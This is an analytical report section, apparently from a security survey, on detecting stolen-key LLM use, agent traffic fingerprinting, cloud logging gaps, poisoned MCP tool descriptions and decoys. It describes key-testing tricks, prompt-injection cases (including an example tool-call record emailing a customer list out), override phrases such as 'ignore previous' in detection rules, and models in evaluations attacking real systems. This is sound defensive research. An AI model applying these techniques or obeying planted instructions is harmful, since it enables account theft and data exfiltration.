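In *Whisper Leak*, McDonald and Bar Or (2025) set the easier goal of detecting one topic among many. They wrote 100 versions of a question about whether money laundering is legal and sent each version 100 times to each of 28 models. They mixed these with 11,716 unrelated questions from Quora and trained classifiers on the sizes and timing of the encrypted replies. They projected the results to a setting with 10,000 other conversations for each one on the target topic. For 17 of the 28 models, the classifiers would find 5 to 20% of the conversations on that topic without flagging any others.

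There is some reason to doubt the 100% precision. For four of the models, precision falls from 100% at a recall of 20% to 10.5% at a recall of 50%. A single false alarm among about 2,340 background questions, a fifth of the total, would produce that drop. There would be 4.27 false alarms per 10,000 conversations against 0.5 correct detections, and 0.5 / (0.5 + 4.27) is 10.5%. So "100%" probably means that the classifier raised no false alarm in a sample of roughly that size, which is too small to establish a false-positive rate below one in 10,000. McDonald and Bar Or advise reading the projections conservatively.

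Topic detection could help identify unauthorised use in a narrow case, such as when a shop's support chatbot should only discuss orders but its encrypted replies look like answers about programming. But the shop can read its own chatbot's logs, so it would rarely need to guess from packet sizes. OpenAI and Microsoft also added random padding after McDonald and Bar Or reported the leak. In tests, padding, sending tokens in batches and injecting fake packets each made the classifiers less successful but did not stop them entirely. A detector that relies on this leak would become less accurate as providers improved users' privacy.

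*Exposing LLM User Privacy via Traffic Fingerprint Analysis* (Zhang, Deng and colleagues, 2025) studies agents rather than chatbots. Its system, AgentPrint, divides encrypted traffic into short time slices, counts the packets and bytes in each, and feeds the counts to a neural network. Different activities produce different traffic patterns. An agent that generates an image sends a little text, pauses and then sends a large burst, while a web search produces one burst for retrieval and another for the summary.

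AgentPrint identified which of 50 known agents was in use with an F1 score of 0.866, averaged over the agents. F1 is the harmonic mean of precision and recall, with a maximum of 1. The score for identifying the type of activity was 0.924. When the traffic could also come from agents outside the known set, the median score for identifying agents stayed above 0.80. These results are impressive for a method that reads no content, but Zhang and colleagues designed their prompts to bring out each agent's main function. An email-writing agent that answers a casual health question produces much more generic traffic, so everyday use would probably be harder to classify.

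The researchers also tried to infer users' occupations from the agents they used. For 49 volunteers, the system's top three guesses included the correct occupational category 69.1% of the time. This result comes closest to showing who is using an agent, but it is still weak evidence, because someone who steals a programmer's key may well be a programmer too.

Fingerprints of this kind could help a company find an agent it hasn't approved, but they may not be reliable enough by themselves. Canale and Soulis explain that every agent has a "behavioural twin", the same program communicating with a service that isn't AI. In their small test on one workstation, two rules based only on behaviour flagged every twin. Their own detector also used the identity of the remote service, and it flagged no twins while detecting every agent in most runs. The test examined how programs behaved on the machine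 rather than packet sizes, so it doesn't refute AgentPrint's results, but it suggests that identifying the service matters more than describing the behaviour more cleverly.

None of these studies tested whether use was authorised. Encrypted traffic can suggest which agent is running, what kind of task it is doing and sometimes what the reply is about. It can't show whether the credential was stolen or whether the user asked the agent to send a particular email. An approved agent's traffic looks much the same whether or not its task is approved.

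### The limits of learned detection

Network security researchers have long tried machine learning, hoping that with enough data it would find subtle differences that people overlook. It has been less successful than the volume of research suggests.

In *Outside the Closed World* (2010), Robin Sommer and Vern Paxson observed that researchers had published a great deal on learned anomaly detection, yet operators rarely used it. They argued that machine learning is better at recognising more of what it has already seen than at finding something new, which is what anomaly detection is meant to do. They also cited the serious consequences of errors, the shortage of training data, the wide variation in normal traffic, and the difficulty of testing a detector.

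"Outside the Closed World" (2010) describes a "semantic gap" in network intrusion detection. A detector reports that something is unusual, but the operator needs to know whether it is an attack, and the answer depends partly on local policy. The gap is wider for agents. An email sent by an agent may not be unusual at all, and whether it is theft depends on a specific request from a manager.

*Pragmatic Assessment of Machine Learning for Network Intrusion Detection* (Apruzzese et al., 2023) reported that practitioners still viewed scientific advances in this area with scepticism. Three years later, *Reshaping Research on Network Intrusion Detection Systems* (Apruzzese, 2026) found that research results still hardly reach practice. It attributes this to a misunderstanding of how such systems work in the field. For instance, some evaluations involve no experiment on a network, not even a synthetic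 one, and many papers measure how well a classifier labels individual samples, although security staff work through high-level reports.

An alert that reads "tool call 4,117 scored 0.93" gives an analyst almost no basis for judging whether an agent's call was authorised. A report that shows the manager's request next to the agent's calls might let the analyst decide in a minute.

Training data is also a problem. According to *ST-GAT* (2026), the field's early benchmark datasets had unrealistic proportions of attacks and no encrypted traffic. A widely used successor from 2018 is more realistic but has labelling errors. It contains over 16 million flows, generated by 50 attacking machines and a simulated organisation with 420 machines and 30 servers. Its attacks include floods of traffic, password guessing and botnets, and a detector trained on them would learn little about an ordinary request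 sent with a stolen key. *Lost in Translation* (2026), a position paper that hasn't been peer reviewed, describes intrusion detection research as almost entirely incomparable and irreproducible. Its evidence comes from a few public datasets, so it doesn't establish that claim for the whole field.

Learned detection may still work on model and tool traffic. Sommer and Paxson were writing about the methods of 2010, and language models can now compare a request with an action in ways those methods couldn't. But their argument implies that a detector needs the request to make that comparison, and that collecting more packets won't supply it.

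### What carries over from network detection

Much of network detection remains useful, including its signatures, baselines and ways of measuring errors. The main changes are in what the detector treats as one event and what other information it needs, such as a record of earlier calls. A network detector may track a connection for a few minutes, but an agent might read the customer list in the morning and email it in the afternoon. A detector monitoring the agent has to link those two calls, and it can't rely on a session identifier to do so.

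| | What carries over | What must change |
|---|---|---|
| Unit of analysis | Grouping small events into a larger record, as flows group packets | The record should cover a session, with all the model requests and tool calls that belong to one task |
| Features | Size, timing, volume and destination, as cheap early signs | Add the credential, model, tool name and arguments, and the meaning of the text |
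| Memory across requests | Counters, connection tracking and baselines | Track where data came from and where it went, over hours if necessary |
| Knowledge of the permitted task | Lists of approved machines, users and services | Add a record of what the user asked for and what the owner of the endpoint or tool allows |

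## Where to watch and what to record

Packets seldom show who sent a request or why, so a defender needs records from the six main places that handle the request itself.

| Observation point | What its records can show | What they miss | Who controls it |
|---|---|---|---|
| User's machine | Which program contacted a model, under whose login, and what commands it ran | Use of a stolen key on another machine | The employer, or the employee on a personal laptop |
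| Cloud administrative log | Which credential called which model, when and from what address; changes to settings | Prompts and answers | The cloud customer, within the options that the cloud company offers |
| Model invocation log | Prompts, answers and token counts | The person behind a shared credential; what the agent's tools actually did | The cloud customer |
| Gateway | The person or program, the prompt, and often the tool calls | Requests that bypass it | The organisation |
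| Model provider | Activity across many customers' accounts | What each account holder permitted; what happens after the answer | The provider |
| Tool server | The tool, its arguments and its result | The conversation that led to the call | Whoever runs the server, sometimes an outside company |

### Following one stolen key

Suppose the shop runs its support chatbot on Amazon Bedrock, a service through which Amazon Web Services (AWS) sells access to models from several companies. The chatbot's requests go through the shop's gateway. One of the shop's developers has a long-term key to the same cloud account and has accidentally published it in some code. At three in the morning, a thief on a rented server uses her key to have a model translate a long document.

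The developer's laptop is asleep and has no record of the request, though it may contain evidence of how the key leaked. The gateway has no record either, because the thief contacted Bedrock directly. Nor do the shop's tool servers, because the translation needs no tools, and a thief who ran an agent would normally connect it to his own servers.

The administrative log records the developer's user name, the ID of her key, the thief's IP address and the model. An analyst could easily think the developer was working late from a hotel. If the shop keeps a model invocation log, it contains the document and the translation, which clearly have nothing to do with the shop's orders. Because AWS runs the model in this case, it may also be able to notice requests from the same address made with other customers' keys.

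If the shop requires all model requests to go through the gateway, a request that appears in AWS's log but not in the gateway's violates that rule. It might still have come from an employee who bypassed the gateway because it was slow.

### What AWS records by default

CloudTrail, AWS's administrative log, is on from the moment a customer opens an account. AWS's *Monitor Amazon Bedrock API calls using CloudTrail* explains that it logs ordinary model calls made through the `bedrock-runtime` endpoint by default. A sample entry gives the user name, key ID, time, source address, client software and model. Its response field is empty, and no field contains the prompt.

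When a model streams its answer, CloudTrail adds a second entry with the token counts. The example in the documentation has 18,694 input tokens and 356 output tokens, which would cost about 6 cents at $3 per million input tokens and $15 per million output tokens. Both entries have the same event name, user and address, so a simple count of entries includes each streamed call twice. For example, if the gateway logged 10,000 requests in a day, 4,000 of them streamed, and CloudTrail has 14,020 entries, the totals differ by 4,020. The second entries for streamed calls account for 4,000 of that difference, so at most 20 requests are missing from the gateway's log.

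Prompts and answers go in a different log. AWS's *Monitor model invocation using CloudWatch Logs and Amazon S3* states that this log is off by default. Once the customer switches it on, each entry contains the caller's identity, the model, the token counts, and the text sent and received. The log covers one Region, AWS's term for a geographic group of data centres. In the May 2026 theft that CrowdStrike reported, requests went to several regions, so a log in only one would have missed some of them. The listed fields don't include the caller's address, so an analyst needs both logs. The request ID in each entry should allow the analyst to match them.

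AWS now has a second model endpoint, `bedrock-mantle`, with different defaults. Customers must turn on logging of model calls there and pay extra for it, according to AWS's *Monitor bedrock-mantle API calls using CloudTrail*.

| Record | Calls through `bedrock-runtime` | Calls through `bedrock-mantle` |
|---|---|---|
| CloudTrail entry for each ordinary model call | On by default | Off by default |
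| Prompt and answer in the invocation log | Off by default | Not available |

With default account settings, therefore, neither log records model calls made through `bedrock-mantle`. The calls still show up in the bill, but that is a slow way to discover misuse. A company that wants the text of those calls has to record it elsewhere, for instance in its gateway. Even after the owner switches logging on, searches for only the older endpoint's event names miss activity on the newer one. Tool calls have a similar gap, because AWS leaves request logging off by default in AgentCore Gateway, its gateway for agents.

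An intruder with administrative rights can turn off the invocation log. According to detection.fyi's *AWS Bedrock Model Invocation Logging Disabled or Modified*, that one action can disable every detector that depends on the log. CloudTrail records the change, so the owner can find it there. AWS requires the invocation log to be stored in the same account as the model calls, so someone who takes over the account may be able to reach the log. The owner should therefore keep a copy elsewhere.

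The contents of logs can also change without the customer doing anything. Until 8 July 2024, CloudTrail gave an error code and message for Bedrock calls that failed validation. In *Bedrock Slip*, Sysdig describes noticing a change and asking AWS about it. That November, Bedrock's engineers told Sysdig that the new behaviour was intended but not yet documented. A detection rule that relied on those errors could have stopped working in the meantime.

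### Finding agents that nobody approved

Cloud logs don't help if an employee installs an agent without telling anyone and connects it to a personal model account. Most of the evidence is then on the employee's machine. Canale and Soulis built Agent Detector, an open-source Windows program, to look for it there.

Agent Detector runs once an hour. It reads the lists that Windows keeps of running programs, open connections and recently looked-up network names, along with installed software and configuration files. It compares these with a catalogue of 39 AI tools and 184 entries for model services. A program that is connected to a model service and has also started a command shell counts as a probable agent. This rule is most useful for home-made scripts, which have no installer or product name. Agent Detector doesn't read prompts or block anything, but it shows the user a notice about the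 company's AI policy and records that the user acknowledged it.

The test of Agent Detector mentioned earlier took place in November 2026 and used 12 synthetic agents and 9 harmless workloads, 3 of which were behavioural twins. The researchers ran everything five times. Agent Detector found every agent in most runs and flagged none of the harmless workloads. The two rules based only on behaviour found 9 and 10 of the agents, and each flagged the twins and an ordinary software installation.

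A perfect score on only 12 agents is compatible with a true detection rate as low as 74%. The test also favoured Agent Detector, because the researchers had twice corrected the program after seeing its mistakes on the same agents and workloads, and they began scanning within seconds of each agent starting.

Scans at random moments did much worse, detecting an agent that called its model every ten seconds in only 15 of 40 attempts. Repeating the scans makes up for some of this. If the agent worked all day and the scans were independent, eight hourly scans would have about a 98% chance (1 − 0.625⁸) of detecting it at least once.

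That calculation applies to a provider with its own network addresses. If a provider shares its addresses with other services, Agent Detector can recognise a connection only while Windows stores the provider's name, for five minutes at most. An hourly scan will usually miss an agent that opens one such connection and keeps it open. The program also missed an agent that used an unlisted relay, one that ran for five seconds, and one inside a virtual machine.

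Agent Detector could not have caught the thief in the shop's case unless the thief had installed it.

### What a useful record contains

In the earlier example, an agent emailed a customer list to Pat because of an instruction hidden in Pat's report. A record of that tool call with all the useful fields might look like this:

```json
{"time": "2026-11-12T09:41:07Z",
 "credential_id": "key-7F3A",
 "person": "sales-manager-12",
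 "agent": "office-assistant",
 "session": "s-4471",
 "approved_task": "Summarise Pat's report",
 "model": "model-a",
 "input_tokens": 5200,
 "output_tokens": 90,
 "tool": "send_email",
 "arguments": {"to": "pat@consultancy.example",
               "attachment": "customers.csv"},
 "result": "sent"}
```

An analyst can see the problem at once because the approved task was to write a summary, but the agent sent an email with the customer list attached. Without the `approved_task` field, the record would look like that of any other email.

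No single observation point supplies all of these fields. The gateway or the provider can record the credential ID, the model and the token counts. The tool server can record the tool, its arguments and the result. The host application tracks who is logged in and which calls belong to each session, so it has to pass those identifiers along. The credential field should hold an ID, never the secret, because anyone who can read the log could steal the secret.

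The approved task is the hardest field to fill. The host should record it when the user makes the request, before the agent reads any documents that might contain planted instructions.

The `person` field doesn't show who made a request when people share a credential. Suppose five developers and the chatbot all use one key. CloudTrail records the same user name for all six, and for anyone who steals the key. The shop doesn't know which developer to ask about a strange request, and it can't revoke the key without stopping the chatbot.

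A gateway can similarly hide who made a request. If it calls Bedrock under one identity for all users, AWS's logs attribute every request to the gateway and show the gateway's address as the source. Only the gateway's log can then connect a request to a person, and only if the gateway made each person log in.

Bedrock's invocation log can link each request to an employee in two ways. The log records the caller's identity with a session name, so a gateway can open a separate session for each employee and use the employee's ID as the name. The gateway can also attach tags, such as a user ID, to each request. AWS fills in every other field of the log entry, but the caller writes the tags, so a thief who has the gateway's credential can put someone else's ID in them.

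### Gateways as targets

A company that routes everything through a gateway also keeps its provider keys in one place, often next to a log of everyone's prompts.

Tom's Hardware lists a breach of LiteLLM, which makes open-source gateway software, among the third-party failures behind the unauthorised access to Claude Mythos. It repeats an allegation, first reported by TechCrunch, that fake security credentials from Delve, one of LiteLLM's suppliers, caused the breach. Delve provides compliance certification, so "credentials" presumably means certificates rather than access keys. A false certificate can discourage customers from checking for weaknesses themselves, although it doesn't give an intruder access.

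An intruder who controls a gateway can send requests with the company's real keys from the usual address, so the source will look normal in the provider's log. The intruder may also be able to delete the matching entries from the gateway's log. The company can still find these requests by comparing the two logs, because they will appear only in the provider's. The comparison also works if the intruder copies the keys and uses them elsewhere, and in that case the source address changes too. The comparison fails if the intruder forges convincing gateway entries, which is a good reason to send each entry to a separate system as soon as the gateway writes it.

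### Recorded but not noticed

Even a complete log helps detect an intrusion only if someone examines it. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes the review that uncovered break-ins by its own models. Anthropic examined the transcripts of 141,006 test runs and found that six involved unauthorised access to real organisations, or about one in 23,500. The earliest incident dated from April, and Anthropic had identified all three by 24 July, the day after the review began.

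The evidence of the earliest incident had therefore been in the transcripts for at least twelve weeks, and finding it took about a day. In all four runs of one incident, the model wrote explicitly in its reasoning that the system it was attacking was real, and then continued.

Anthropic acknowledges that real-time monitoring would have helped reveal the problem sooner. Speed mattered most for the malicious Python package, which was online for about an hour. Investigators could later count the systems that had run it, but only an alert within that hour could have protected them. Anthropic reached two of the three affected organisations, and neither had detected the intrusion.

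The quick search in July doesn't prove that a live detector would have worked. The reviewers had just learned from OpenAI's disclosure to look for a model reaching the internet from a test environment that should have been sealed off. Someone building a live detector would have had to think of that beforehand. The fourth case, which came to light by September, suggests that the July reviewers either missed something or didn't check everything.

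### The privacy cost of keeping content

Anthropic could search its old tests because it had kept their full text. For a business, a log of the full text of every prompt and answer is a liability. Prompts can include customers' complaints, source code and legal advice, so a thief may want the log more than the model access it was meant to protect. Any analyst who can search the log can also read colleagues' work.

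Monitoring can be intrusive even when it doesn't record content. Canale and Soulis warn that hourly findings about an employee add up to a timeline of when that person works with an agent. They point out that French law requires an employer to tell employees about such a monitoring system before using it to collect information about them.

One compromise is to store the result of a content check instead of the content. In AWS's sample entry for Bedrock's content filters, CloudTrail records that the filters matched violence with high confidence and blocked an email address, without including any of the text. But this rules out later searches of the text for things the filters weren't set to detect, and Anthropic found its incidents in July through such a search.

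Many business customers of model providers had an arrangement called zero data retention, under which the provider analyses prompts and outputs and then discards them. Anthropic ended it for its most capable models in June 2026. *Data retention practices for Covered Models* requires the company to keep prompts and outputs from these models for 30 days, because some attacks become visible only across many requests. For example, someone might send hundreds of slight variations of a forbidden prompt in the hope that one works. Anthropic's staff can read a conversation only in limited circumstances, such as after an automated flag, and a tamper-proof log records each access.

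Regulated companies still objected. Help Net Security's *Anthropic’s Enterprise Frontier Safeguards lets your Claude logs stay in your cloud* (2026) explains that they would have had to notify their own customers, rework contracts and satisfy internal rules on sensitive material. Anthropic announced a new arrangement, Enterprise Frontier Safeguards, on 1 September and opened a public beta on 23 November.

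Anthropic's *Developing Enterprise Frontier Safeguards with our customers* claims that its system combines the privacy of zero data retention with the ability to detect misuse across sessions and accounts. The customer can keep the prompts and answers in its own cloud storage, under its own encryption keys. Metz, in *Anthropic introduces zero data retention option for firms using advanced AI*, reports that they stay there for 30 days and that Anthropic's software, run by the cloud service, scans them from time to time for signs of serious misuse, including stolen credentials. This should be better at catching someone using stolen credentials than checking each request and discarding it, because the software can compare requests over time.

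When the software finds something, it alerts the customer's security team with a report called a Safety Case. Anthropic also gets an alert but can't open the related data, according to Metz. Help Net Security's *Anthropic wants to catch rogue AI activity without retaining your data* (2026) notes that a Safety Case contains neither prompts nor responses. Exame's *Empresas poderão usar o Claude sem deixar dados com a Anthropic* (2026) adds that even the customer's own staff can't read the stored records directly. An analyst alerted about the developer's key would probably need a separate log to see what the thief had asked for. A company that wants to investigate its alerts may therefore store the text twice.

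Exame reports that on Anthropic's own platform, the system covers requests through the main messages interface but doesn't automatically cover uploaded files, batch results or sessions of Anthropic's managed agents.

Anthropic's announcement gives no figures for how many stolen keys the system catches or how many false alarms it raises. The customers it quotes mostly praise their control over the data rather than the detection. Keeping data for thirty days may also be too short to catch slow or unexpected misuse. If Anthropic had deleted its test transcripts after 30 days, its July review could not have found the transcript of the April incident.

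OpenAI still offers zero data retention to eligible customers of its most advanced models. Metz reports that it is also testing "private inference", which would hide prompts and answers from OpenAI even while its systems process them. A provider using private inference could presumably still count requests and tokens, but any check of their content would have to happen on the customer's side.

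## Detection by known signs of intrusion

Once an organisation keeps usable logs, it can search them automatically with signatures, like the rule for Code Red. To write a signature, an analyst starts from the records of a real intrusion and picks out a detail that other intruders will probably leave too but legitimate users seldom do. A model name would be a poor choice because legitimate requests include one too, and so would an odd phrase from one thief's prompt, because other thieves won't repeat it.

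The rule's writer then expresses the detail as conditions on log fields, and a program checks each new entry against them. Running the rule on a few months of old entries first gives a rough estimate of how many legitimate entries it would flag.

### A rule from 2024

In May 2024, Sysdig published an early case of LLMjacking. Both the intruders' methods and the logs have changed since then, but the case is small enough to follow from start to finish.

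The intruders took cloud credentials from a web server that ran a vulnerable version of Laravel, a framework for building websites. They had a script that tested credentials against ten AI services. On Amazon Bedrock, they sent a model request that set the maximum reply length to −1 tokens. The request was certain to fail, but the error showed whether the credential could use the model. Bedrock returned `AccessDenied` if the credential lacked permission, and `ValidationException` if it had permission and the model was switched on. No model ran in either case, so the test added nothing to the owner's bill.

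The attackers also queried Bedrock to check whether the account logged prompts and answers. Some requests came from a client that matched OAI Reverse Proxy, open-source software that lets many people share a pool of keys. Its developers promise that, for "privacy", it won't use an AWS key with that logging enabled.

Sysdig's rule raises a warning when an entry in CloudTrail, AWS's administrative log, meets three conditions:

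```text
service    = Bedrock
event name = InvokeModel
error code = ValidationException
```

| Log entry | Error code | Does the rule match? |
|---|---|---|
| The shop's chatbot answers a customer | None | No |
| A thief tests a key that works | `ValidationException` | Yes |
| A thief tests a key that has no access | `AccessDenied` | No |
| A developer mistypes a setting | `ValidationException` | Yes |

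The rule can flag a developer's innocent mistakes, because Bedrock returns a validation error for many kinds of faulty request. A developer might send a document that is too long for the model, or move a program to a model that expects its settings in a different format. Some software uses −1 to mean "no limit", so a legitimate program could send the same invalid number as the thief.

Suppose the shop's developers cause 90 validation errors in a month and a thief causes one. The rule raises 91 alerts, and one is real. Suppose the rule also requires that the same credential was used to query the logging settings within an hour of the error. A developer fixing a faulty request has little reason to do that, so perhaps one of the 90 errors meets the condition by coincidence. The analyst then gets two alerts, one of them caused by the thief. But a thief who never queries the logging settings,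 or who waits until the next day, would not trigger the rule. Requiring an address that is new to the credential instead would catch that thief, but it would also flag developers who make mistakes while working from a hotel.

CloudTrail stopped reporting these errors nine weeks after Sysdig published the rule. A rule that has stopped working produces no alerts, so it looks the same as a working rule with nothing to find. An owner can check that the rule still works by sending a harmless request each week that should trigger it and confirming that the alert arrives.

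Intruders also changed their methods. One group that Google tracked in 2026 tested keys by sending valid requests for a one-token reply, which cause no error. A new rule could look for such requests in the log of prompts and answers, which records the caller's limit on reply length. But legitimate programs also request single tokens, for instance to sort messages into category A or B, so this rule would also need a second condition.

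### Signs that need no prompt content

An intruder can easily reword a test request, but has to switch on a service that is off before using it. An analyst can look for account changes like this without reading any prompts.

| Sign | An honest cause | A condition that narrows it |
|---|---|---|
| Someone switches on an AI service | A team starts a new project | The credential has never changed settings before |
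| Someone creates a key or service account | Routine replacement of an old key | The new credential calls an expensive model within minutes |
| Someone reads or changes the logging settings | An audit | The request doesn't come from the auditors' account |
| The client identifies itself as a known resale proxy | An employee experiments with the same software | The request comes from outside the company |

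In 2024, AWS customers had to request access to each model, which Sysdig described as a speed bump for intruders rather than a security mechanism. Where a platform still has this requirement, it helps detection because the intruder's access request is logged before they send any prompts.

The client name is much weaker evidence because the caller chooses it. The invalid request in Sysdig's published log entry came from Boto3, AWS's Python library, which many legitimate scripts also use. A client name that identifies a resale proxy should trigger an alert, but an ordinary client name is almost no evidence either way.

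A reseller who checks for logging and avoids accounts that have it will leave when the owner turns it on, so the owner may deter this kind of intruder without recording any of their prompts.

### Poisoned and altered tool descriptions

A malicious tool can influence a model before anyone calls it, because the model first reads the descriptions of all the available tools. Beretta and colleagues give the example of a tool named `daily_quote`, which supplies an inspirational quotation. Its description also tells the model to add a hidden 0.5% fee whenever it uses a separate payment tool, and to send the money to the attacker. The attack doesn't require the user to ask for a quotation. Trail of Bits' *We built the security layer MCP always needed* calls this "line jumping", because the instruction reaches the model before the user can approve or refuse a call.

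Models have often obeyed malicious instructions placed in tool descriptions. *Machine Learning-Based Detection of MCP Attacks* (Mattsson, Nyberg and colleagues, 2026) cites MCPTox, a 2025 benchmark that added poisoned descriptions to 45 real servers. The attacks succeeded 36.5% of the time on average across 20 widely used models.

Nobody knows how common poisoned descriptions are outside the laboratory. Kraishan (2026), in *Same Name, Different Server*, searched the source code of 14,353 servers from the public MCP registry for telltale phrases and found no poisoned descriptions. Kraishan's upper limit of about 0.03% of servers is probably too low, because the scanner could extract tool definitions from only 4,238 of the 13,051 code repositories it covered. Counting only those 4,238 repositories, and assuming one server in each, raises the limit to about 0.09%. Both limits apply only to openly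 worded poisoning, since Kraishan acknowledges that the scanner would miss disguised instructions.

*MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to the protocol, defines a rug pull as an attack in which a server is useful and trustworthy at first but changes later. The server's operator, or someone who has taken it over, may replace the tool descriptions, alter the tools' code or redirect calls to another machine. According to *MCP-38*, current clients don't alert users when a tool's definition changes.

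Innocent changes are common. Of the 8,900 servers in Kraishan's census with more than one published version, 36% had changed their registry description. A change of host is another sign to watch for, and 370 of the servers had moved their remote endpoint to a different host under the same name. Kraishan thinks most of these moves were routine migrations, but neither the registry nor a client can distinguish a migration from a takeover.

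These figures cover each server's short summary in the registry, which is separate from the tool descriptions that a model reads. The registry doesn't store tool definitions, so its data can't show how often they change.

### Comparing fingerprints

The most direct defence against altered descriptions is to keep a record of the approved text. A program can do this with a hash function such as SHA-256, which turns text of any length into a 256-bit number called its fingerprint. The same text always gives the same number, and nobody has found two different texts with the same number.

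When the company first connects to the server, an employee reads and approves the name, description and input schema of the `get_alerts` tool from the earlier example. The program computes a fingerprint of all three and stores it. Each time the server sends its list of tools, the program computes the fingerprint again. If it matches the stored one, the client passes the tool to the model. Otherwise the program withholds the tool until somebody has read the new version.

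The fingerprint has to cover the input schema because a parameter's name alone can cause a model to leak data, as Beretta and colleagues found. A model may fill in a parameter called `summary_of_environment_details` without being told to.

Trail of Bits' mcp-context-protector works in much the same way, except that it stores the approved configuration itself. It blocks every feature of a new server until the user has reviewed it. If one tool later changes, the program blocks only that tool, but if the server's general instructions change, it blocks the whole server.

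A fingerprint reveals every change to the text, including changes written in another language or in invisible characters. Because it doesn't depend on what the text means, it can't show whether a change is harmful. Correcting a spelling mistake in `get_alerts` changes the fingerprint just as completely as adding an instruction to steal files.

The work this creates depends on how often descriptions change. *Registry Descriptions Go Stale Unevenly* (Bharti, 2026) tracked the official registry for 89 days and found that 3.3% of servers changed their registry description within 30 days. In the last month, nearly 19,000 entries had about 39 changes a day, or about two per 1,000 entries. If tool descriptions change at the same rate, which Bharti didn't measure, a company with 50 servers would have about three changes a month to review. That is manageable, but the operator of a catalogue of thousands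 of servers would face dozens a day. Trail of Bits warns that users who see too many of these alerts start to miss real attacks or switch the protection off. It suggests that security engineers review the changes centrally when servers change often.

Careless programming can also cause false alarms. When Bharti compared 781 stored fingerprints with freshly computed ones, 34 differed only because one program had removed surrounding spaces from the text before hashing it and the other hadn't.

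The code behind a tool can change while its description stays the same. *ProbeID* (2026) tries to detect such changes by sending a tool the same question at different times and comparing the answers. In every repeat from day 22 onward, the same seven tools gave changed answers, although all the servers still reported their original version numbers. In a simulated rug pull, a check based on this method cut the share of corrupted calls from 6.3% to 1.7%.

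The check rejected only three of seven tools that had changed on the server side. The method can't work for some tools, such as one that reports current conditions and so gave a different answer every time.

### Pattern rules

A pattern rule matches particular words or arrangements of characters, so it can be applied to a description that nobody has approved before. The matched text also shows the analyst the reason for the alert, such as a reference to a file that usually holds passwords. *MCP-Guard* (Xing, Qi and colleagues, 2025) uses such rules as the first of three stages. The rules match phrases like "ignore previous", the paths of sensitive files, and an "IMPORTANT" tag that often appears in published examples of poisoned descriptions.

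A rule that looks for "ignore previous" won't match "disregard what you were told earlier", which means the same thing to a model. Adding rules helps only until an attacker finds another paraphrase, and there are many. Beretta and colleagues add that an attacker can encode an instruction so that the suspicious words don't appear but the model can still decode it.

Pattern rules can also examine the calls themselves. In *MCP security risks*, Mooney, who works for the log-monitoring vendor Datadog, recommends checking tool arguments for characters such as semicolons, which can be used to add a second command to a database query or command line. Semicolons are rare in a tool that searches support tickets, but legitimate database queries often end with one, so a company has to set this rule separately for each tool. Mooney suggests combining it with a rule for sudden increases in calls, since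 a burst of calls followed by strange arguments is better evidence than either alone. A list of exceptions can keep test servers from triggering too many alerts.

To measure how much the type of pattern matters, Kraishan checked 42 alerts by hand for each of seven kinds of weakness in servers' code. When the evidence was in the wording itself, as with a program that accepts any version of a library, 93% of the alerts were correct. For command injection, where the danger depends on whether the program later runs a piece of text as a command, 17% were correct. Poisoned tool descriptions are closer to command injection, because an instruction such as "You must call this tool first" may be an attack or the only way to make the tool work.

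### Trained classifiers

A classifier learns from labelled examples of malicious and harmless descriptions, so nobody has to list the suspicious phrases in advance. The second stage of MCP-Guard is a classifier of this kind, a language model that Xing and colleagues trained for the purpose. In the third stage, a general-purpose language model labels the text safe, unsafe or uncertain. If the label is uncertain, MCP-Guard uses the classifier's score instead.

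Xing and colleagues assembled 70,448 attack samples, 97% of which combine templates with instructions that GPT-4 generated. For the tests, they used 2,153 malicious samples and 3,105 harmless tool descriptions, and held a fifth of them out of training. The counts below correspond to their published percentages, with GPT-4o-mini, a small OpenAI model from 2024, as the third stage.

| Detector | Attacks caught, of 432 | False alarms, of 621 | Average time |
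|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Pattern rules alone | 168 | 4 | 2 ms |
| Trained classifier alone | 404 | 14 | 55 ms |
| Rules and classifier | 406 | 17 | 49 ms |
| All three stages | 430 | 40 | 506 ms |

Six of the rule sets had an average recall of 98.6% when each was tested separately on the kind of attack it was meant for. On the whole test set, the rules together caught only 38.9% of attacks. This is partly because Xing and colleagues tightened the rules to avoid false alarms, since an alarm in the first stage blocks the text immediately.

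The third stage is meant partly to reduce false alarms, but in this test it more than doubled them, from 17 to 40, while catching 24 more attacks. Whether that is worthwhile depends on how rare attacks are. If one description in 1,000 were malicious, about one alert in 66 from the full system would be real. MCP-Scan, a competing tool in the same test, missed 62 attacks but raised only one false alarm. With the same share of malicious descriptions, about one in three of its alerts would be real, although a single false alarm is too few to estimate its false alarm rate with any confidence.

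These results come from the 2025 version of the paper. Xing and colleagues published a revised version in July 2026. A newer model in the third stage might well do better.

Mattsson and colleagues reported even higher scores in April 2026. Their 1,440 descriptions included malicious ones from MCPTox and harmless ones from the code of popular servers. They created more training examples by automatically translating descriptions into four Asian languages and back. Before translating, they set aside 142 descriptions for testing so that the training data would contain no translated copies of test items.

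Cisco's published pattern rules caught 10 of the 48 malicious descriptions in the test and flagged 6 of the 94 harmless ones. All three trained classifiers classified every description correctly. One was a support vector classifier, a much older and simpler method that uses how often each word occurs.

A word-counting method got a perfect score, which suggests the test was easy. All the malicious descriptions came from one collection and all the harmless ones from elsewhere, so a classifier could succeed by learning to recognise the collection. Mattsson and colleagues found that words such as "must" and "should" counted as signs of malice, and they accept that a description unlike those in MCPTox could escape detection. Even for descriptions of this kind, a perfect score on 48 attacks and 94 harmless texts is compatible with a true recall of 93% and a true false-positive rate of 4%.

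They also built their classifier into a program that examines a tool after the model chooses it, just before the call. This is too late to catch line jumping. The `daily_quote` tool does its damage without being chosen, so the program would never examine its description. The check should run when the client first receives the description.

Fingerprints can make classifiers more practical, because only new and changed descriptions need checking. The company with three changes a month would get about one false alarm every five months at a false-positive rate of 6.4%, the rate of the full MCP-Guard system. Someone still has to read each change, because a classifier may miss a careful paraphrase too.

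### Decoys

A decoy is something that looks valuable to an intruder but no legitimate user has a reason to use. Any use of it is suspicious, so the owner doesn't have to predict what an attack will look like.

The simplest sign of intrusion to set up is the use of a planted key. The organisation creates a key that has no permissions and leaves it in a private code repository. An intruder who copies the repository will probably test every key in it, and the first attempt to use the planted key triggers an alert, even if the request is invalid or asks for a single token. If each repository contains a different planted key, the organisation can also tell which repository leaked. A new developer who tries the key in good faith can cause a false alarm, as can a security tool that checks whether exposed keys still work.

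On a tool channel, the owner can offer a decoy tool, perhaps called `export_payroll_archive`, that returns nothing and raises an alert when called. Listing the tool should not raise the alert, because clients routinely fetch the whole list of tools. A decoy tool is less reliable than a decoy key because an agent chooses tools by their descriptions. If a manager asks for last year's payroll, an agent in legitimate use may well call the decoy. The alert should therefore include the user's request.

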